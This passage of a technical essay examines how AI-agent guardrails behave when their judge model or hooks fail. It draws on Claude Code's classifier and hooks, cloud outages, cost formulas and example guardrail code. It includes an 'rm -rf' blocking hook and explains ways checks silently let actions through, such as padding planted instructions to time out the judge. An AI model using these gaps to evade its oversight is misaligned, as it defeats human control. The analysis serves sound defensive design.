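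An unparseable classifier response also stops the action, and a retry usually succeeds. In this case, Claude Code doesn't show its usual notification or add the action to the list of recently blocked actions, where a user could approve it. This makes sense because there is no classifier decision for the user to overrule.

If the conversation is too long for the classifier, Claude Code tries to shorten it by replacing earlier parts with a summary. If that isn't possible, it asks the user whether to run the action, or doesn't run it if the session is unattended. This is the only failure in the table where a person immediately decides whether an unreviewed action runs.

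Anthropic exempts refused classifier requests from both limits but doesn't mention the other failures, such as outages. Outages probably don't count toward the limits either, because the limits apply when "the classifier blocks an action", and a classifier that is down hasn't blocked anything.

### One message for two different events

The exemption for refused requests dates from version 2.1.225. Before that, Claude Code counted a refused request as a block and sent Claude the same rejection message as for a genuine block. According to the release note, reproduced in NewReleases' *github anthropics/claude-code v2.1.225*, Claude Code now also tells the model to move on rather than retry. Classmethod, a Japanese IT company, covered the fix on 8 August in its summary *Claude Code v2.1.225~v2.1.226 Major Updates* (2026).

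Suppose a programmer is repairing a server after a break-in and pastes the attacker's script into the conversation. Claude then tries to restart the web server, which is harmless. Claude Code sends the conversation to the classifier, but a safety filter on Anthropic's API (the interface through which programs reach its models) refuses the request because of the pasted script, so the classifier never assesses the restart.

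Under the old behaviour, Claude would be told that the restart was too dangerous. It might then try to reload the configuration, or stop and start the server in two steps. Each attempt would fail the same way, because the script would still be in the conversation. After the third refusal, auto mode would pause and the programmer would have to approve actions by hand, under the impression that the agent had just tried three dangerous things. If the programmer approved the restart, auto mode would resume, and the next three checks would probably trigger another pause. Under the older rule, the third refusal would have ended an unattended run.

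The guardrail failed closed throughout, so no unchecked action ran. The harm came from a false explanation, which led Claude to look for a safer command when no command would have helped and gave the programmer a reason to distrust the next genuine block. In August 2026 Anthropic argued that the classifier was useful by citing a customer's figure that about 10% of its sessions since mid-May had included a classifier denial. Most of that period preceded the fix, so the figure could include refused requests unless someone separated them from actual denials.

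Claude Code still denies the action, but the programmer can switch to another permission mode and approve it by hand, or start a new conversation without the script so that the classifier works again. Azure OpenAI's filter can reject a judge's prompt for the same kind of reason, and Copilot Studio's default setting then lets the agent proceed.

### When every check fails

When a fault persists, a guardrail that fails closed keeps blocking the actions it checks, as two bugs show. Before version 2.1.216, an expired login token made every classifier request fail, and auto mode denied every checked action until Claude Code got a new token. Claude Code now refreshes the token and retries once. Until version 2.1.229, auto mode also failed on every tool call for users who had switched off a header that Claude Code attaches to its requests. Classmethod's *Claude Code v2.1.228~v2.1.229 Major Updates*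 (2026) concluded that auto mode must have been unusable for organisations with that setting.

These users lost working time but, as Saltzer and Schroeder would have expected, they could hardly have missed the problem.

### Ten responses without a verdict

In many sessions Claude Code no longer sends its own requests to the classifier. It asks Anthropic's server to check the actions as part of the request in which Claude proposes them. The program then has to interpret three situations:

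- A response arrives complete but without any review results, perhaps because a company's gateway removed them. Claude Code assumes that the server doesn't review this session and goes back to sending its own classifier requests.
- A response breaks off before the results arrive, or the results are unreadable. Claude Code denies the action.
- The server's check fails for one action, for example because it times out. Claude Code denies that action too.

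None of these counts as approval. Since a change on 6 November, Claude Code has handled the first situation more strictly in some sessions, including those behind gateways with certain background features switched off. If the server can't check an action in one of these sessions, Claude Code now asks the user or denies the action, unless the user has chosen the built-in classifier in advance.

Until version 2.1.280, Claude Code immediately denied each action that received no verdict, and never stopped. During a long outage, Claude could presumably keep proposing actions and using up tokens without getting anything done. Claude Code now waits before some of the denials to delay the next attempt, and stops after ten responses in a row without a verdict. In an interactive session, the user sees a warning and can start again with a new message, which resets the count. An unattended run ends with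 an error. A subagent, a second agent given part of the task by Claude, stops early, and Claude receives whatever it had produced with a note about the stop.

The separate count matters because a person would respond differently to blocks than to missing verdicts. Three blocks in a row suggest a problem with the agent or the classifier's rules, while ten missing verdicts suggest a problem with the connection.

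Claude Code also denies an action that has changed since its review. Suppose the server approves a command to delete a folder called `build`, and a hook then rewrites the command to delete `build-archive`. The approval covered only the original command, so Claude Code refuses to run the new one and tells Claude that a hook changed it. Claude can propose the call again for a fresh review. This denial doesn't count toward the ten.

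### A subagent's report arrives anyway

The classifier reviews a subagent's task before it starts, each risky action while it works, and all its work and its final report before the main agent reads the report. The classifier fails closed on the actions but not on the final review. If it is unavailable for that review, the main agent still receives the report, with a note to verify the work before acting on it.

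Withholding the report would add less protection than blocking an action, because the subagent has already finished and the classifier has already checked each of its risky actions. Any risky action the main agent takes next also needs approval. But the final review exists because a subagent may have read planted instructions partway through its task and carried them into its report. Without the review, the main agent has to notice those instructions itself, with only the note as a warning.

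Even a flagged report reaches the main agent, with a security warning at the top. Anthropic also attaches a warning when a separate safety check refuses the review, so the main agent is warned about a report that nobody has found suspicious. This is a milder form of the confusion that version 2.1.225 removed for actions.

Until 3 November 2026, auto mode's missing verdicts were also harder to see for a subagent's tool calls, because nothing appeared in the user's main view. Anthropic's changelog for that day lists a new notice for these cases.

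### A hook that crashes

A hook lets a company or programmer add their own check. Claude Code runs the hook at a chosen event, such as just before a tool call, and passes it a JSON description of the call. The simplest kind of hook reports its result through its exit code, a number that every program returns when it ends. By convention, 0 means success and any other number means failure.

In Anthropic's *Hooks reference*, the code for a deliberate block is 2. With 0, the call proceeds unless the hook has printed a decision against it. Any other code is normally a "non-blocking error", after which the call also proceeds. This short Python program shows what follows from that:

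```python
import json, sys

call = json.load(sys.stdin)
if "rm -rf" in call["tool_input"]["command"]:
    print("rm -rf is not allowed", file=sys.stderr)
    sys.exit(2)
```

The program reads the description and looks for `rm -rf`, a command that deletes a folder and everything in it. If it finds the command, it exits with code 2 and Claude Code blocks the call. If the field `command` had a different name, Python would raise a KeyError and, because the program has no handler, end it with exit code 1. Claude Code would then let the deletion proceed, whereas the twelve-line example needed an explicit handler to allow calls after its own errors.

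Anthropic warns that a hook exiting with code 1 does not block the tool call, since 1 is the usual code for failure on Unix systems and a programmer might expect it to block. A mistyped path has the same effect: the hook never runs, the shell reports a code such as 127, and the tool call goes ahead. The user sees a notice that the hook failed, which is more than the twelve-line example offers, but the notice helps only if someone is watching.

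An ordinary hook that hangs before a tool call doesn't block the call either. By default, Claude Code waits 600 seconds, then cancels the hook and lets the call continue. However, a hook that times out while checking a change of model blocks the change, as does a timeout in a callback, a check function that developers register through Anthropic's Agent SDK.

A hook can also run on a web server and answer over HTTP. Claude Code treats any status outside the 200s as a non-blocking error, including 403 ("Forbidden"), the natural choice for a refusal. To block the call, the server has to return a status in the 200s and put the refusal in the body of its reply.

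"Goes ahead" means that the call continues to the normal permission checks. In auto mode the classifier may still stop it, and in Manual mode the user may. A failed hook therefore removes one of several checks, but a hook often enforces a company rule that the classifier doesn't cover. In `bypassPermissions` mode, which runs almost everything without asking, a hook may be the only check on a command apart from fixed rules. Anthropic reported in August 2026 that 25% of interactive sessions started in this mode.

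### The onFailure setting

Since version 2.1.295 (8 October 2026, according to the changelog), users can set `"onFailure": "block"` on a hook to stop the action if the hook fails. The table shows the effect on a hook that runs before a tool call.

| What happens | Without the setting | With `"onFailure": "block"` |
|---|---|---|
| The hook exits with 2 | Blocked | Blocked |
| The hook crashes with code 1 | Goes ahead | Blocked |
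| The script is missing | Goes ahead | Blocked |
| The hook times out | Goes ahead | Blocked |
| An HTTP hook answers 403 | Goes ahead | Blocked |
| The hook exits with 0 after printing malformed JSON in braces | Goes ahead | Blocked |
| The hook exits with 0 after printing a greeting and then a refusal in JSON | Goes ahead | Goes ahead |

The last row can occur when a user's shell prints a line of text every time it starts. Claude Code reads a hook's output as JSON only if the output contains nothing else. If that line comes before the hook's refusal, Claude Code treats all of the output as plain text, which counts as neither a decision nor a failure. A hook that blocks by exiting with code 2 doesn't have this problem.

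The setting also can't detect a hook that fails but reports success. Anthropic's sample script for blocking `rm` commands extracts the command with a program called jq. If jq isn't installed, the script gets an empty string, finds no `rm` in it and exits with 0. Anthropic tells readers to install jq first, but a colleague who copies the script to a new computer may not know that. To prevent this, the script would have to check whether it had read a command, and exit with 2 if it hadn't.

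Anthropic offers `onFailure` for command hooks and HTTP hooks. On 3 November it added a version for Agent SDK callbacks, which already blocked a tool call when they timed out, but not when they failed in other ways. Hooks that send a prompt to a Claude model for a decision are also judge-model guardrails, but they have no such field. Until 8 October 2026, these hooks could allow what they should have blocked if a user wrote the prompt as an instruction, such as "Block commands that…". Anthropic's changelog doesn't explain the cause, but an error setting wouldn't catch a hook that returns the wrong decision.

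On Windows, the default can depend on whether Git Bash, a command shell that comes with Git for Windows, is installed. If it is missing, certain hooks run in PowerShell instead, and a failure blocks the tool call even if `onFailure` isn't set. Once someone installs Git for Windows, the same hooks fail open with the same configuration. A hook that blocks the call after a crash on one company laptop could therefore let it through on another. Setting `onFailure` explicitly removes the difference.

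Anthropic hasn't changed the general default, probably because many existing hooks rely on it. Some scripts exit with 1 just to print a warning, and a stricter default would turn each warning into a block. Other parts of Claude Code have become stricter. Since 14 October, for instance, it blocks an action if a plugin's hook can't receive it or return an answer.

### How reliable the human fallback is

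Auto mode hands the decision back to a person after repeated blocks or when a conversation is too long to check. How safe this is depends on how carefully people read permission prompts. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports an experiment on this.

A research vendor recruited 1,053 paid professional testers for a coding study in a purpose-built test environment. They knew they were being evaluated, but not on which behaviour. Partway through each session, a clearly dangerous command replaced the text of one permission prompt, and the vendor recorded whether the tester approved it. The command never ran, even if approved. The testers blocked 143 of the 1,053 commands (13.6%), while auto mode blocked 937 of the same commands (89%).

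Anthropic also gives the number of commands that only one of the two blocked, and the rest of this table follows by subtraction.

| | Tester blocked | Tester approved |
|---|---|---|
| Auto mode blocked | 137 | 800 |
| Auto mode allowed | 6 | 110 |

A system that required approval from both the testers and auto mode would have stopped 943 commands, only six more than auto mode alone. The top row is more relevant to the pause after repeated blocks, when Claude Code asks a person about the kind of action the classifier has just been blocking. In the experiment, the testers approved 800 of the 937 commands that auto mode blocked, or 85%. A real user might do better because the pause itself is a warning, which the testers didn't get.

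When the classifier couldn't review a dangerous command, asking a person would have been much closer to failing open than to failing closed. Asking the testers stopped 143 of the 1,053 dangerous commands, whereas denying them all would have stopped every one and allowing them all would have stopped none.

The testers blocked about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session, but only about 5% after 50 or more prompts. People in auto mode see far fewer prompts, so their attention should hold up better, but even 17% is low.

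All these numbers come from Anthropic's own post announcing auto mode as the default, so the company had an interest in the result. The testers had no code of their own at stake and may have assumed that nothing could go wrong in a test environment, though knowing they were being evaluated may have made them more careful. The commands were clearly dangerous, which probably helped the classifier. In the earlier test, it missed a larger share, 17%, of the 52 real cases. Anthropic doesn't report how many harmless commands auto mode would have blocked in this experiment.

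Figures from ordinary use suggest the same. Users approve 97% of permission prompts, although most of those are presumably for harmless commands. Among sessions that Anthropic's safety systems had flagged, a seriously harmful action that the user hadn't explicitly requested occurred in 6.3% of those with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. A model graded the sessions. Users chose their own mode, so the difference may partly reflect different tasks.

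However, users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents for whole tasks. Plans are rarer than permission prompts, and users may reject them for reasons unrelated to safety, but the figure suggests that people read when the question is worth their time. A fallback prompt with one clear question about the unreviewed action, and a notice that no check had taken place, might therefore do better than the prompts in the experiment.

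## The argument for letting traffic through when a check fails

When persistent faults made Claude Code's auto mode deny every checked action, the affected users lost working time. The same kind of fault does far more damage in the infrastructure behind websites and apps, where one failing check can block millions of requests. Google and Cloudflare both had outages of this kind in 2025, and both promised afterwards that some of their checks would fail open. Their experience is the best argument for line 12 in the twelve-line example.

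### Google's quota check

Google Cloud rents computing power and storage to other companies, whose programs send it requests over the internet. Service Control, a Google program, checks whether each request is authorised and within the customer's usage quota. Ventrata's *Google Cloud APIs Degradation* (2025), a status notice from a Google customer, reproduces Google's full report on how this program failed.

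On 29 May 2025, Google added a new quota check to Service Control. The code had no handler for missing data. Google released it one region at a time, but the fault did not appear because the faulty part ran only after a certain kind of policy change. On 12 June, at about 10:45 Pacific time, such a change introduced a policy with blank fields. Google's database copied it around the world within seconds. In every region, Service Control read the blank fields, crashed, restarted and crashed again.

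Google's engineers found the cause within ten minutes and had switched off the new check everywhere within 40 minutes. Most regions then began to recover, but in the Iowa region the restarting copies of Service Control overloaded their shared database, and recovery took up to two hours and 40 minutes. The whole incident lasted three hours, according to preliminary Google figures reported in TrustLayer's *Google Cloud Major Outage* (2025).

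According to BTW Media's *One policy, every region*, existing streaming and infrastructure resources were not directly affected, but requests failed for many products, including Cloud Storage and the service that manages access rights. Ventrata had trouble with checkout orders and payments. The outage also took down Google's status service, so customers waited about an hour for the first notice, and some had lost the monitoring that would have alerted them sooner.

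Google promised to split Service Control into separate parts that fail open, so that it can still serve requests when one check fails. It had already ended the outage in much the same way, by manually bypassing the faulty quota check. If that check had failed open from the start, some customers might have exceeded their limits for a while, but Google could probably have measured the excess and charged for it later. That would have done much less harm than a worldwide outage. Failing open is harder to justify for Service Control's other task, authorisation, because letting unauthorised requests through could expose customers' data. Google didn't discuss this difference, but it presumably had checks like the quota check in mind.

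### Cloudflare's bot score and firewall

Cloudflare carries traffic between websites and their visitors and filters out attacks. Its Bot Management module uses a machine-learning model to score how likely each request is to come from a program rather than a person. The model does a similar job to a judge model, though it doesn't write verdicts.

Cloudflare (2025) traced its outage of 18 November 2025 to a change in database permissions at 11:05 UTC. The change made a query return duplicate rows, which more than doubled the number of entries in a file listing the traits its bot-detection model uses. The bad file reached the whole network because Cloudflare rebuilds and distributes the file every few minutes to keep up with bot operators' changing tactics. Cloudflare's proxy, the software that passes requests on, had room for 200 traits and normally used about 60. The new file exceeded that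 limit, and the newer version of the proxy crashed because its code had no handler for the error.

Visitors to Cloudflare customers' sites saw error pages from about 11:20. Most traffic was flowing again by 14:30, and the last services recovered at 17:06. Cloudflare later said the main failure lasted about two hours and ten minutes, an hour less than the time between 11:20 and 14:30. The company said the outage was its worst since 2019 and stopped most of its core traffic.

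Cloudflare's email filter shows what failing open could have looked like. When it lost one of its sources of sender reputation data, it kept delivering mail with less accurate spam detection, and Cloudflare observed no critical effect on customers.

The older version of the proxy also kept running and let traffic through, but it gave every request a substitute bot score of zero. For customers whose rules blocked likely bots, that score triggered the block and turned away large numbers of real people. A guardrail that replaces a missing verdict with an ordinary-looking value can similarly cause acceptable requests to be blocked or prohibited ones to be allowed.

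The second outage came 17 days later, while Cloudflare was trying to protect customers from a newly disclosed flaw in React, a widely used tool for building websites. According to Cloudflare (2025), its engineers were increasing the amount of each request the firewall could examine. An internal testing tool couldn't handle the larger size, so they switched it off through a system that reaches every server within seconds. This triggered a bug that had gone unnoticed for years in the older proxy. After skipping a rule, the code still tried to read that rule's results, which didn't exist, and raised an error. From 08:47 to 09:12 UTC, the affected sites, which accounted for about 28% of the HTTP traffic Cloudflare serves, returned errors instead of pages.

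After the first outage, Cloudflare promised only to review how its proxy modules fail. After the second, it promised to replace "incorrectly applied hard-fail logic" in its critical systems, so that software given a corrupt configuration file would record the error and either return to a known good state or pass traffic without a score. Two weeks later, Cloudflare wrote in its plan *Code Orange* (2025) that it should not have dropped traffic by default when the bot module failed.

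Cloudflare eventually adopted a less sweeping policy. Its *Code Orange* follow-up of May 2026 describes software that first tries the last configuration that worked. If that isn't possible, the software fails open or closed depending on whether reduced service is better than none. Bot Management now fails open in that case.

The December outage shows why Cloudflare needed that choice. If the whole firewall had failed open, the sites would have stayed up for those 25 minutes, but requests exploiting the React flaw could have reached them. An attacker who breaks into a server in that time may still have access after the firewall recovers. The bug concerned the results of a single test rule, so the software could probably have avoided both problems by discarding those results and still applying the other rules.

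### Kubernetes moved towards failing closed

Kubernetes is software that runs programs across a cluster of computers. All changes to the cluster go through its API server. Before accepting a change, this server can send it to an admission webhook, a separate program that approves, rejects or alters it. If the webhook fails or doesn't answer, the `failurePolicy` setting determines whether the server lets the change through (`Ignore`) or rejects it (`Fail`).

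Kubernetes changed the default from `Ignore` to `Fail` when it moved the webhook settings from the test version, v1beta1, to the stable version, v1. Its *Deprecated API Migration Guide* lists the change without giving a reason. *KEP-492*, the plan for the stable version, cites feature requests and bug reports as its general motivation. Kubernetes' later security advice, *Securing Admission Controllers* (2022), gives a more specific reason to fail closed, which is that it stops attackers from getting around a webhook by disabling it. They could do that by sending it more requests than it can handle.

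The stricter setting can stop a cluster from repairing itself. Suppose a webhook has to approve every program that starts, and the computer it runs on breaks down. Kubernetes tries to start the webhook on another computer. The API server sends the webhook a request to approve this, gets no answer and rejects the change, so the webhook can't start. *Lesson in Kubelings*, a training exercise from iximiuz Labs, reproduces this deadlock from a real outage that the company Jetstack described. Kubernetes' *Admission Webhook Good Practices* warns that two webhooks that check each other can also deadlock if they fail together.

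*Kyverno killed my API server. Again* (zwindler, 2026) describes a related problem that an engineer had during an upgrade in February 2026. An API server restarted but did no useful work, because the webhook of Kyverno, a tool for enforcing rules on clusters, had prevented it from creating one of its own basic network records. The log entry contained "denied the request", followed by details of a failed network connection. Like Claude Code before version 2.1.225, the system reported an error as if it were a policy decision.

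Cloudflare's customers had a similar experience in November. The login page of Cloudflare's control panel used Turnstile, the company's tool for telling people from bots. While Turnstile was down, customers who weren't already logged in couldn't change their settings to get their sites working again.

To avoid such deadlocks, Kubernetes advises operators to exempt the part of the cluster where the webhook runs, rather than fail open everywhere. Repairs can then go ahead while the webhook still checks everything else. Kubernetes does recommend failing open for webhooks that alter changes, provided a second check validates the result. If a webhook that adds a required security setting is down, a change that already has the setting can proceed, and the second check rejects one that lacks it.

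Gatekeeper, another rule-enforcing tool, uses `Ignore` by default in version 3.17. Open Policy Agent's *Failing Closed* explains that a later audit should find any invalid items that entered the cluster during an outage. This works well when an operator can fix the problem by removing a badly configured program the next day, but less well if the program has already copied customer data to an outsider.

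### Outages that people notice

All three outages in 2025 came from bugs or bad data, not from a slow network, so waiting wouldn't have helped. If the checks had failed open, they might have kept letting traffic through until someone repaired them, as with the renamed field in the twelve-line example.

The failures were at least obvious. Google's engineers were working on theirs within two minutes, and an automated test at Cloudflare detected the November fault three minutes after the first errors on customers' traffic. Portal, a small Kubernetes project, fails closed for this reason. Its documentation, *Fail-closed semantics*, says that an operator then learns of a broken check "within minutes instead of months". The estimate is informal, but Saltzer and Schroeder made the same argument in 1975. A company that wants to fail open after a bug therefore needs an alarm to replace the complaints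 that blocked users would have made. Users can then keep working while engineers repair the check.

Failing closed can also lead people to avoid the check. After Cloudflare's November outage, Krebs on Security (2025) published questions for companies to ask themselves, including who had approved emergency routing changes, whether staff had moved work to personal devices or unapproved services, and whether these workarounds had become permanent. A developer whose agent stops all afternoon might similarly disable its guardrail and forget to turn it back on, which would be worse than letting a few unchecked actions through.

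### A safety filter that stopped Gemini

A more recent outage involved a safety filter, which makes it closer to the problem of judge models. Google sells access to its Gemini models through Vertex AI, where one safety-filtering service supports all of them. On 27 February 2026, a configuration change caused certain requests to disrupt this filter and reduce its capacity. Google Cloud (2026) reported that customers saw increased error rates across all Gemini models on Vertex AI for one hour and 58 minutes.

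Customers received the status codes 429 and 503, which normally mean a limit has been reached or a service is unavailable. The codes didn't identify a safety filter as the cause. The errors may also have led some programs to resend requests and add to the load.

Google's remedies were stricter validation during rollouts and better alerts. It had promised eight months earlier that Service Control would fail open, but it made no such promise for the safety filter. Google gave no reason, but the cause of the outage suggests a security concern. If the filter had failed open, anyone who discovered which requests disrupted it could have used them to switch it off, possibly for other customers too, whereas an attacker gains much less from breaking a quota check.

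### What a wrong decision costs

Whether a guardrail should fail open depends on how likely an unchecked item is to be harmful and how much each kind of mistake costs. Let *p* be the probability that an item is harmful when the judge has returned no verdict. Let *H* be the cost of letting a harmful item through and *S* the cost of stopping a harmless one. Failing open costs *pH* per item on average, and failing closed costs (1 − *p*)*S*. Failing open is cheaper if

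*p* < *S* / (*S* + *H*)

The table applies this to two very different guardrails. The amounts are invented for illustration.

| What the judge checks | Cost of wrongly letting it through (*H*) | Cost of wrongly stopping it (*S*) | Failing open is cheaper if *p* is below |
|---|---|---|---|
| The tone of a chat reply | £2 | £1 | 33% |
| Deletion of a database without a backup | £50,000 | £20 | 0.04% |
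| Deletion of a database with a tested backup | £500 | £20 | 3.8% |

In the first row, a shop's assistant answers questions about deliveries, and a judge checks that its replies are polite. Suppose 2% of the replies are rude. During an outage that affects 1,000 replies, failing open sends 20 rude ones and costs £40 in apologies, while failing closed withholds 980 useful answers and costs £980. The shop can apologise for a rude reply, and the main model's training is a second safeguard that keeps most replies polite. A customer who deliberately provokes a rude reply gains little beyond an embarrassing screenshot. Failing open would still be cheaper even if judge errors clustered on rude replies enough to raise *p* to 30%.

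As with the bot score, most of the traffic is harmless, a mistake does limited damage, and the person at the other end won't wait long, so the argument from the outages carries over well. It would not if the same judge also checked for medical advice that could injure someone, because *H* would then be much higher.

In the other two rows, an agent clears out old test databases and asks for permission to delete one. Suppose one deletion in 1,000 would destroy a database that customers are using. If that database has no backup, failing open on 1,000 deletions costs £50,000 on average, while failing closed delays 999 harmless ones at a cost of about £20,000. The average also understates the danger to a small company that couldn't survive the loss. *S* is low compared with *H* because deleting an old database, unlike serving a website visitor, can usually wait until the judge is working again.

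With a tested backup, the expected loss from failing open falls to £500, so even a database deletion doesn't always call for failing closed. But the backup has to be out of the agent's reach, or the agent could delete it too, and someone has to notice the mistake before the backup expires.

An attacker can change the result again, because the figure of one in 1,000 covers only an agent's occasional mistakes. A stranger could plant an instruction to delete the live database and add enough text to make the judge time out. If such attacks account for 5% of the checks that end without a verdict, *p* is above the 3.8% threshold, and failing closed has the lower expected loss even with the backup. An attacker could also wait for an outage instead of causing one, since a provider's public status page could reveal when the judge is down.

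A second check helps only if it still works when the judge is down. Database permissions that prevent the agent from deleting live data would still work. A second judge from the same provider might not, because the same overload or expired password could stop both.

The same agent may send chat replies and delete databases, so a single error setting for all its actions is likely to be wrong for some of them. Copilot Studio's default, for instance, lets a tool call through after an error in the check, whether the tool looks up opening hours or deletes records. For clusters with several webhooks, Kubernetes suggests making critical checks fail closed and allowing less critical ones to fail open. For an agent, this would mean setting the error behaviour separately for each kind of action.

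## Building and testing a guardrail that keeps errors apart from verdicts

A guardrail's code must recognise a judge error before it can handle that error differently for a chat reply and a database deletion. The twelve-line example can't do this because it returns "allow" both after an approval and after an error. In the version below, one function calls the judge and another determines what happens to the action.

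```python
 1  def get_verdict(action):
 2      try:
 3          reply = ask_judge(action, timeout=5)
 4          verdict = json.loads(reply)["verdict"]
 5      except Exception as error:
 6          return "no verdict", type(error).__name__
 7      if verdict in ("allow", "block"):
 8          return verdict, None
 9      return "no verdict", "unknown label"
10
11  def decide(action, verdict, cause):
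12      if verdict == "allow":
13          return "run"
14      if verdict == "block":
15          return "stop"
16      record_missing_verdict(action, cause)
17      if action.tool in LOW_RISK and cause in TEMPORARY:
18          return "run"
19      return "hold"
```

The first function returns "allow", "block" or "no verdict", and includes a cause with "no verdict". Its handler on line 5 is as broad as the old one, but it reports the error instead of treating it as "allow". Line 7 accepts only the two expected words, so if the judge starts to write "deny", the function now returns "no verdict" with the cause "unknown label".

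The second function contains the policy for missing verdicts, which uses two lists that the developer fills in. `LOW_RISK` might contain the tool that looks up a shop's opening hours, and `TEMPORARY` might contain exceptions that usually resolve on their own, such as a TimeoutError. A refund without a verdict always ends in "hold". A request for opening hours goes ahead after a timeout but not after a lasting fault such as the renamed field.

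### Return values and exceptions

The code that runs the tools acts on the decision:

```python
verdict, cause = get_verdict(action)
decision = decide(action, verdict, cause)
if decision == "run":
    run_tool(action)
elif decision == "stop":
    raise PolicyBlock(action)
else:
    hold_for_review(action, cause)
```

An ordinary return value goes only to the caller, so a broad exception handler further up can't catch it. A retry helper has no exception to wrap, and a task group passes the value through unchanged as the task's result. The tool also runs only in the branch for "run", so if a programmer misspells one of the other decisions, the action is put on hold.

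*LACUNA* (2026), a system in which a language model writes pieces of a program while the program runs, has a related problem with exceptions. When the model can't produce code that compiles, the call raises an exception. A handler around an outer call also catches these failures from nested calls, even unrelated ones. The alternative, `agentSafe`, returns either the result or the error details as a value, so the caller can handle each failure where it occurs.

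If a caller forgets to check a return value, the program carries on, whereas an unhandled exception would stop it. A caller can also check the value incorrectly. In Python, `if get_verdict(action):` is true for every outcome, including a block, because the function returns a pair of values and Python treats any pair as true. The best protection is probably to let only one function call `run_tool`, so that reviewers have a single place to check.

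If a block should end the agent's whole run, the "stop" branch should still raise an exception, because an exception can pass through many layers of code without each one having to forward a message. If a handler further up catches and ignores it, the agent may carry on and try something else, but the blocked action has not run. In the plug-in loop described earlier, ignoring the exception led straight to `run_tool`. A program should also raise an exception at start-up if its judge gives the wrong verdict on either of two test items, one harmless and one forbidden. This check would catch a mistyped model name before any customer used the program.

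### What a retry can and cannot repair

The cheapest response to a missing verdict is to ask again. If 2% of judge calls fail and the failures are independent, the chance that two in a row fail is 0.02 × 0.02 = 0.0004, or 0.04%. In 10,000 checks, one retry reduces the missing verdicts from 200 to 4. But the result depends heavily on why the calls fail:

| Cause of the 200 failures | Missing verdicts after one retry |
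|---|---|
| Independent network faults | 4 |
| An overloaded judge that fails half of all second attempts | 100 |
| Conversations too long for the judge | 200 |
| 180 network faults and 20 over-long conversations | 23 |

In the last row, over-long conversations cause 10% of the failures before the retry and about 86% afterwards. The items that still lack a verdict after a retry therefore include a larger share of documents that someone may have made long on purpose, which is a reason to treat a failure after the retry more strictly than a first timeout.

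*ReliabilityBench* (2026), a set of stress tests for agents, sorts faults by whether a retry can succeed. A retry can work after a brief timeout, a reset connection, a soft rate limit or a truncated reply, but not after an account suspension or a change of format. Retries also add delay. Two five-second attempts keep a user waiting ten seconds, and Copilot Studio's one-second deadline leaves hardly any time for a second attempt. Many client libraries also retry automatically. If the library makes up to three attempts per call, a guardrail that retries once can send six requests to a judge that may already be overloaded.

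The guardrail should retry only the judge call, and only when the verdict is missing, never after a block. A second judge call adds only delay and expense, because it changes nothing outside the guardrail. Repeating the action itself is far riskier. In *Idempotency Is Not Recovery*, Xu (2026) deliberately crashed a program that ran an agent's tool calls and replayed its requests. Three simpler versions of the program each carried out the action twice in 117 of 200 such cases. A version that gave each action a permanent identifier and kept a record of unfinished ones never repeated an action.

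### Fallbacks when the judge stays silent

A second judge helps most if it comes from another provider and accepts longer texts, but it may be less accurate. If the first judge detects 95% of harmful actions and the second only 80%, an attacker who can make the first judge time out raises the chance of getting through from 5% to 20%. LiteLLM switches off retries and standard fallbacks for its judge calls so that only the configured judge decides.

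A simple rule that runs locally works even when the network is down. The rule should list what is permitted and refuse everything else, as Saltzer and Schroeder advised. For example, it might allow an agent only to read files inside its project folder. It can't assess context, so it will refuse many actions that a judge would have approved.

When a check ends in an error, the guardrail can also ask a person to decide. However, the testers in Anthropic's experiment approved most of the dangerous commands they saw, and frequent questions make people less careful. At 2,000 checks a day and a 2% error rate, someone would have to answer 40 questions a day. If a format change made every check end in an error, they would have to answer 2,000, too many for anyone to read carefully.

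Holding the action for later review suits work that can wait, such as a refund, but not a chat reply. The program has to check the situation again before it runs a held action, because a colleague may already have paid the refund by hand, for example. A held action also needs an expiry date, after which the program cancels it, or the queue will fill up with forgotten requests. The message to the agent should not present the missing verdict as a block, and Claude Code has followed this practice since version 2.1.225.

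Finally, the agent can continue with fewer tools. *AuthGuard-R* (2026) describes this for robots that take instructions from a language model. If the program that authorises actions hits an error, the robot rejects ordinary mission actions, but a separate policy still permits a few emergency actions, such as stopping, releasing dangerous force, returning to a marked safe position or asking a person for help. A plain "fail closed" rule would be wrong here because a robot that does nothing can be dangerous. A software agent could similarly keep its read-only tools and the ability to ask the user a question. Some combinations of read-only tools are still unsafe. For example, an agent that can read customer records and fetch web addresses can leak the records by including them in an address.

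### Circuit breakers

When a judge is down, every check waits for the full timeout. At five seconds per check, a task with 50 checked actions would wait 250 seconds. A circuit breaker limits this delay by stopping calls to a service that keeps failing. After five failures in a row, for example, it reports an error at once without contacting the judge. After a pause, perhaps a minute, it lets one trial call through and resumes normal service if that call succeeds. The task would then lose about 25 seconds plus an occasional trial, and the judge would have a chance to recover.

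The terms "open" and "closed" are easy to confuse. An "open" breaker has cut the connection, as in electrical wiring, so a guardrail that fails closed can have an open breaker.

While the breaker is open, the code should pass each new action to `decide` as "no verdict" with the cause "breaker open", because the breaker only saves time and doesn't settle what happens to the action. If the guardrail instead skips the check during the pause, five failures are enough to turn it off for everyone. On a service with 20 checks a second, 1,200 actions would go through unchecked in one minute, and an attacker who can cause five timeouts could choose when that happens.

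Timeouts and server errors suggest a problem with the judge, so the breaker should count them as failures. It should not count an over-long conversation, which is a problem with one item, because a single user could then open the breaker for everyone else. A block isn't a failure either, but a breaker wrapped around the original `check` function would count each `PolicyBlock` exception as one, so five correct blocks in a row could cut off a working judge.

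LiteLLM has a similar mechanism called cooldown, which temporarily stops using a model deployment (one configured connection to a model) after repeated failures. Judge calls count towards the cooldown of the deployment they use. If the judge shares a deployment with user traffic, repeated judge failures can take the users' model out of service, even though the guardrail lets their requests through. Giving the judge a separate deployment avoids this.

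### How three gateways expose the choice

Many companies use a gateway that applies guardrails to all their traffic instead of writing this code themselves. Acteon, a gateway for actions such as sending messages, has a single switch called `fail_open`. According to Acteon's *LLM Guardrails*, it defaults to false, so the gateway denies an action if the judge times out, hits a rate limit or returns invalid JSON. The default was true up to version 0.1.x. *LLM Guardrails* justifies the change mainly by arguing that people who turn on a safety check expect it to stop unchecked actions. For a purely advisory check, it suggests setting `fail_open` to true and explaining why in a comment beside it.

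A counter records judge errors in either mode. However, Acteon gives a denied action the outcome "Suppressed" whether the cause was a block or an error. Only the reason text differs, beginning with "LLM guardrail unavailable" for an error, so an application has to read it before explaining the refusal to a user.

AISIX, a gateway from API7, mostly passes text to outside moderation services or applies its own keyword rules. According to AISIX's *Guardrail Behavior*, most guardrails have separate settings for requests (`fail_open`) and responses (`output_fail_open`), both false by default. Like Acteon, AISIX let unchecked requests through by default until version 0.11.0.

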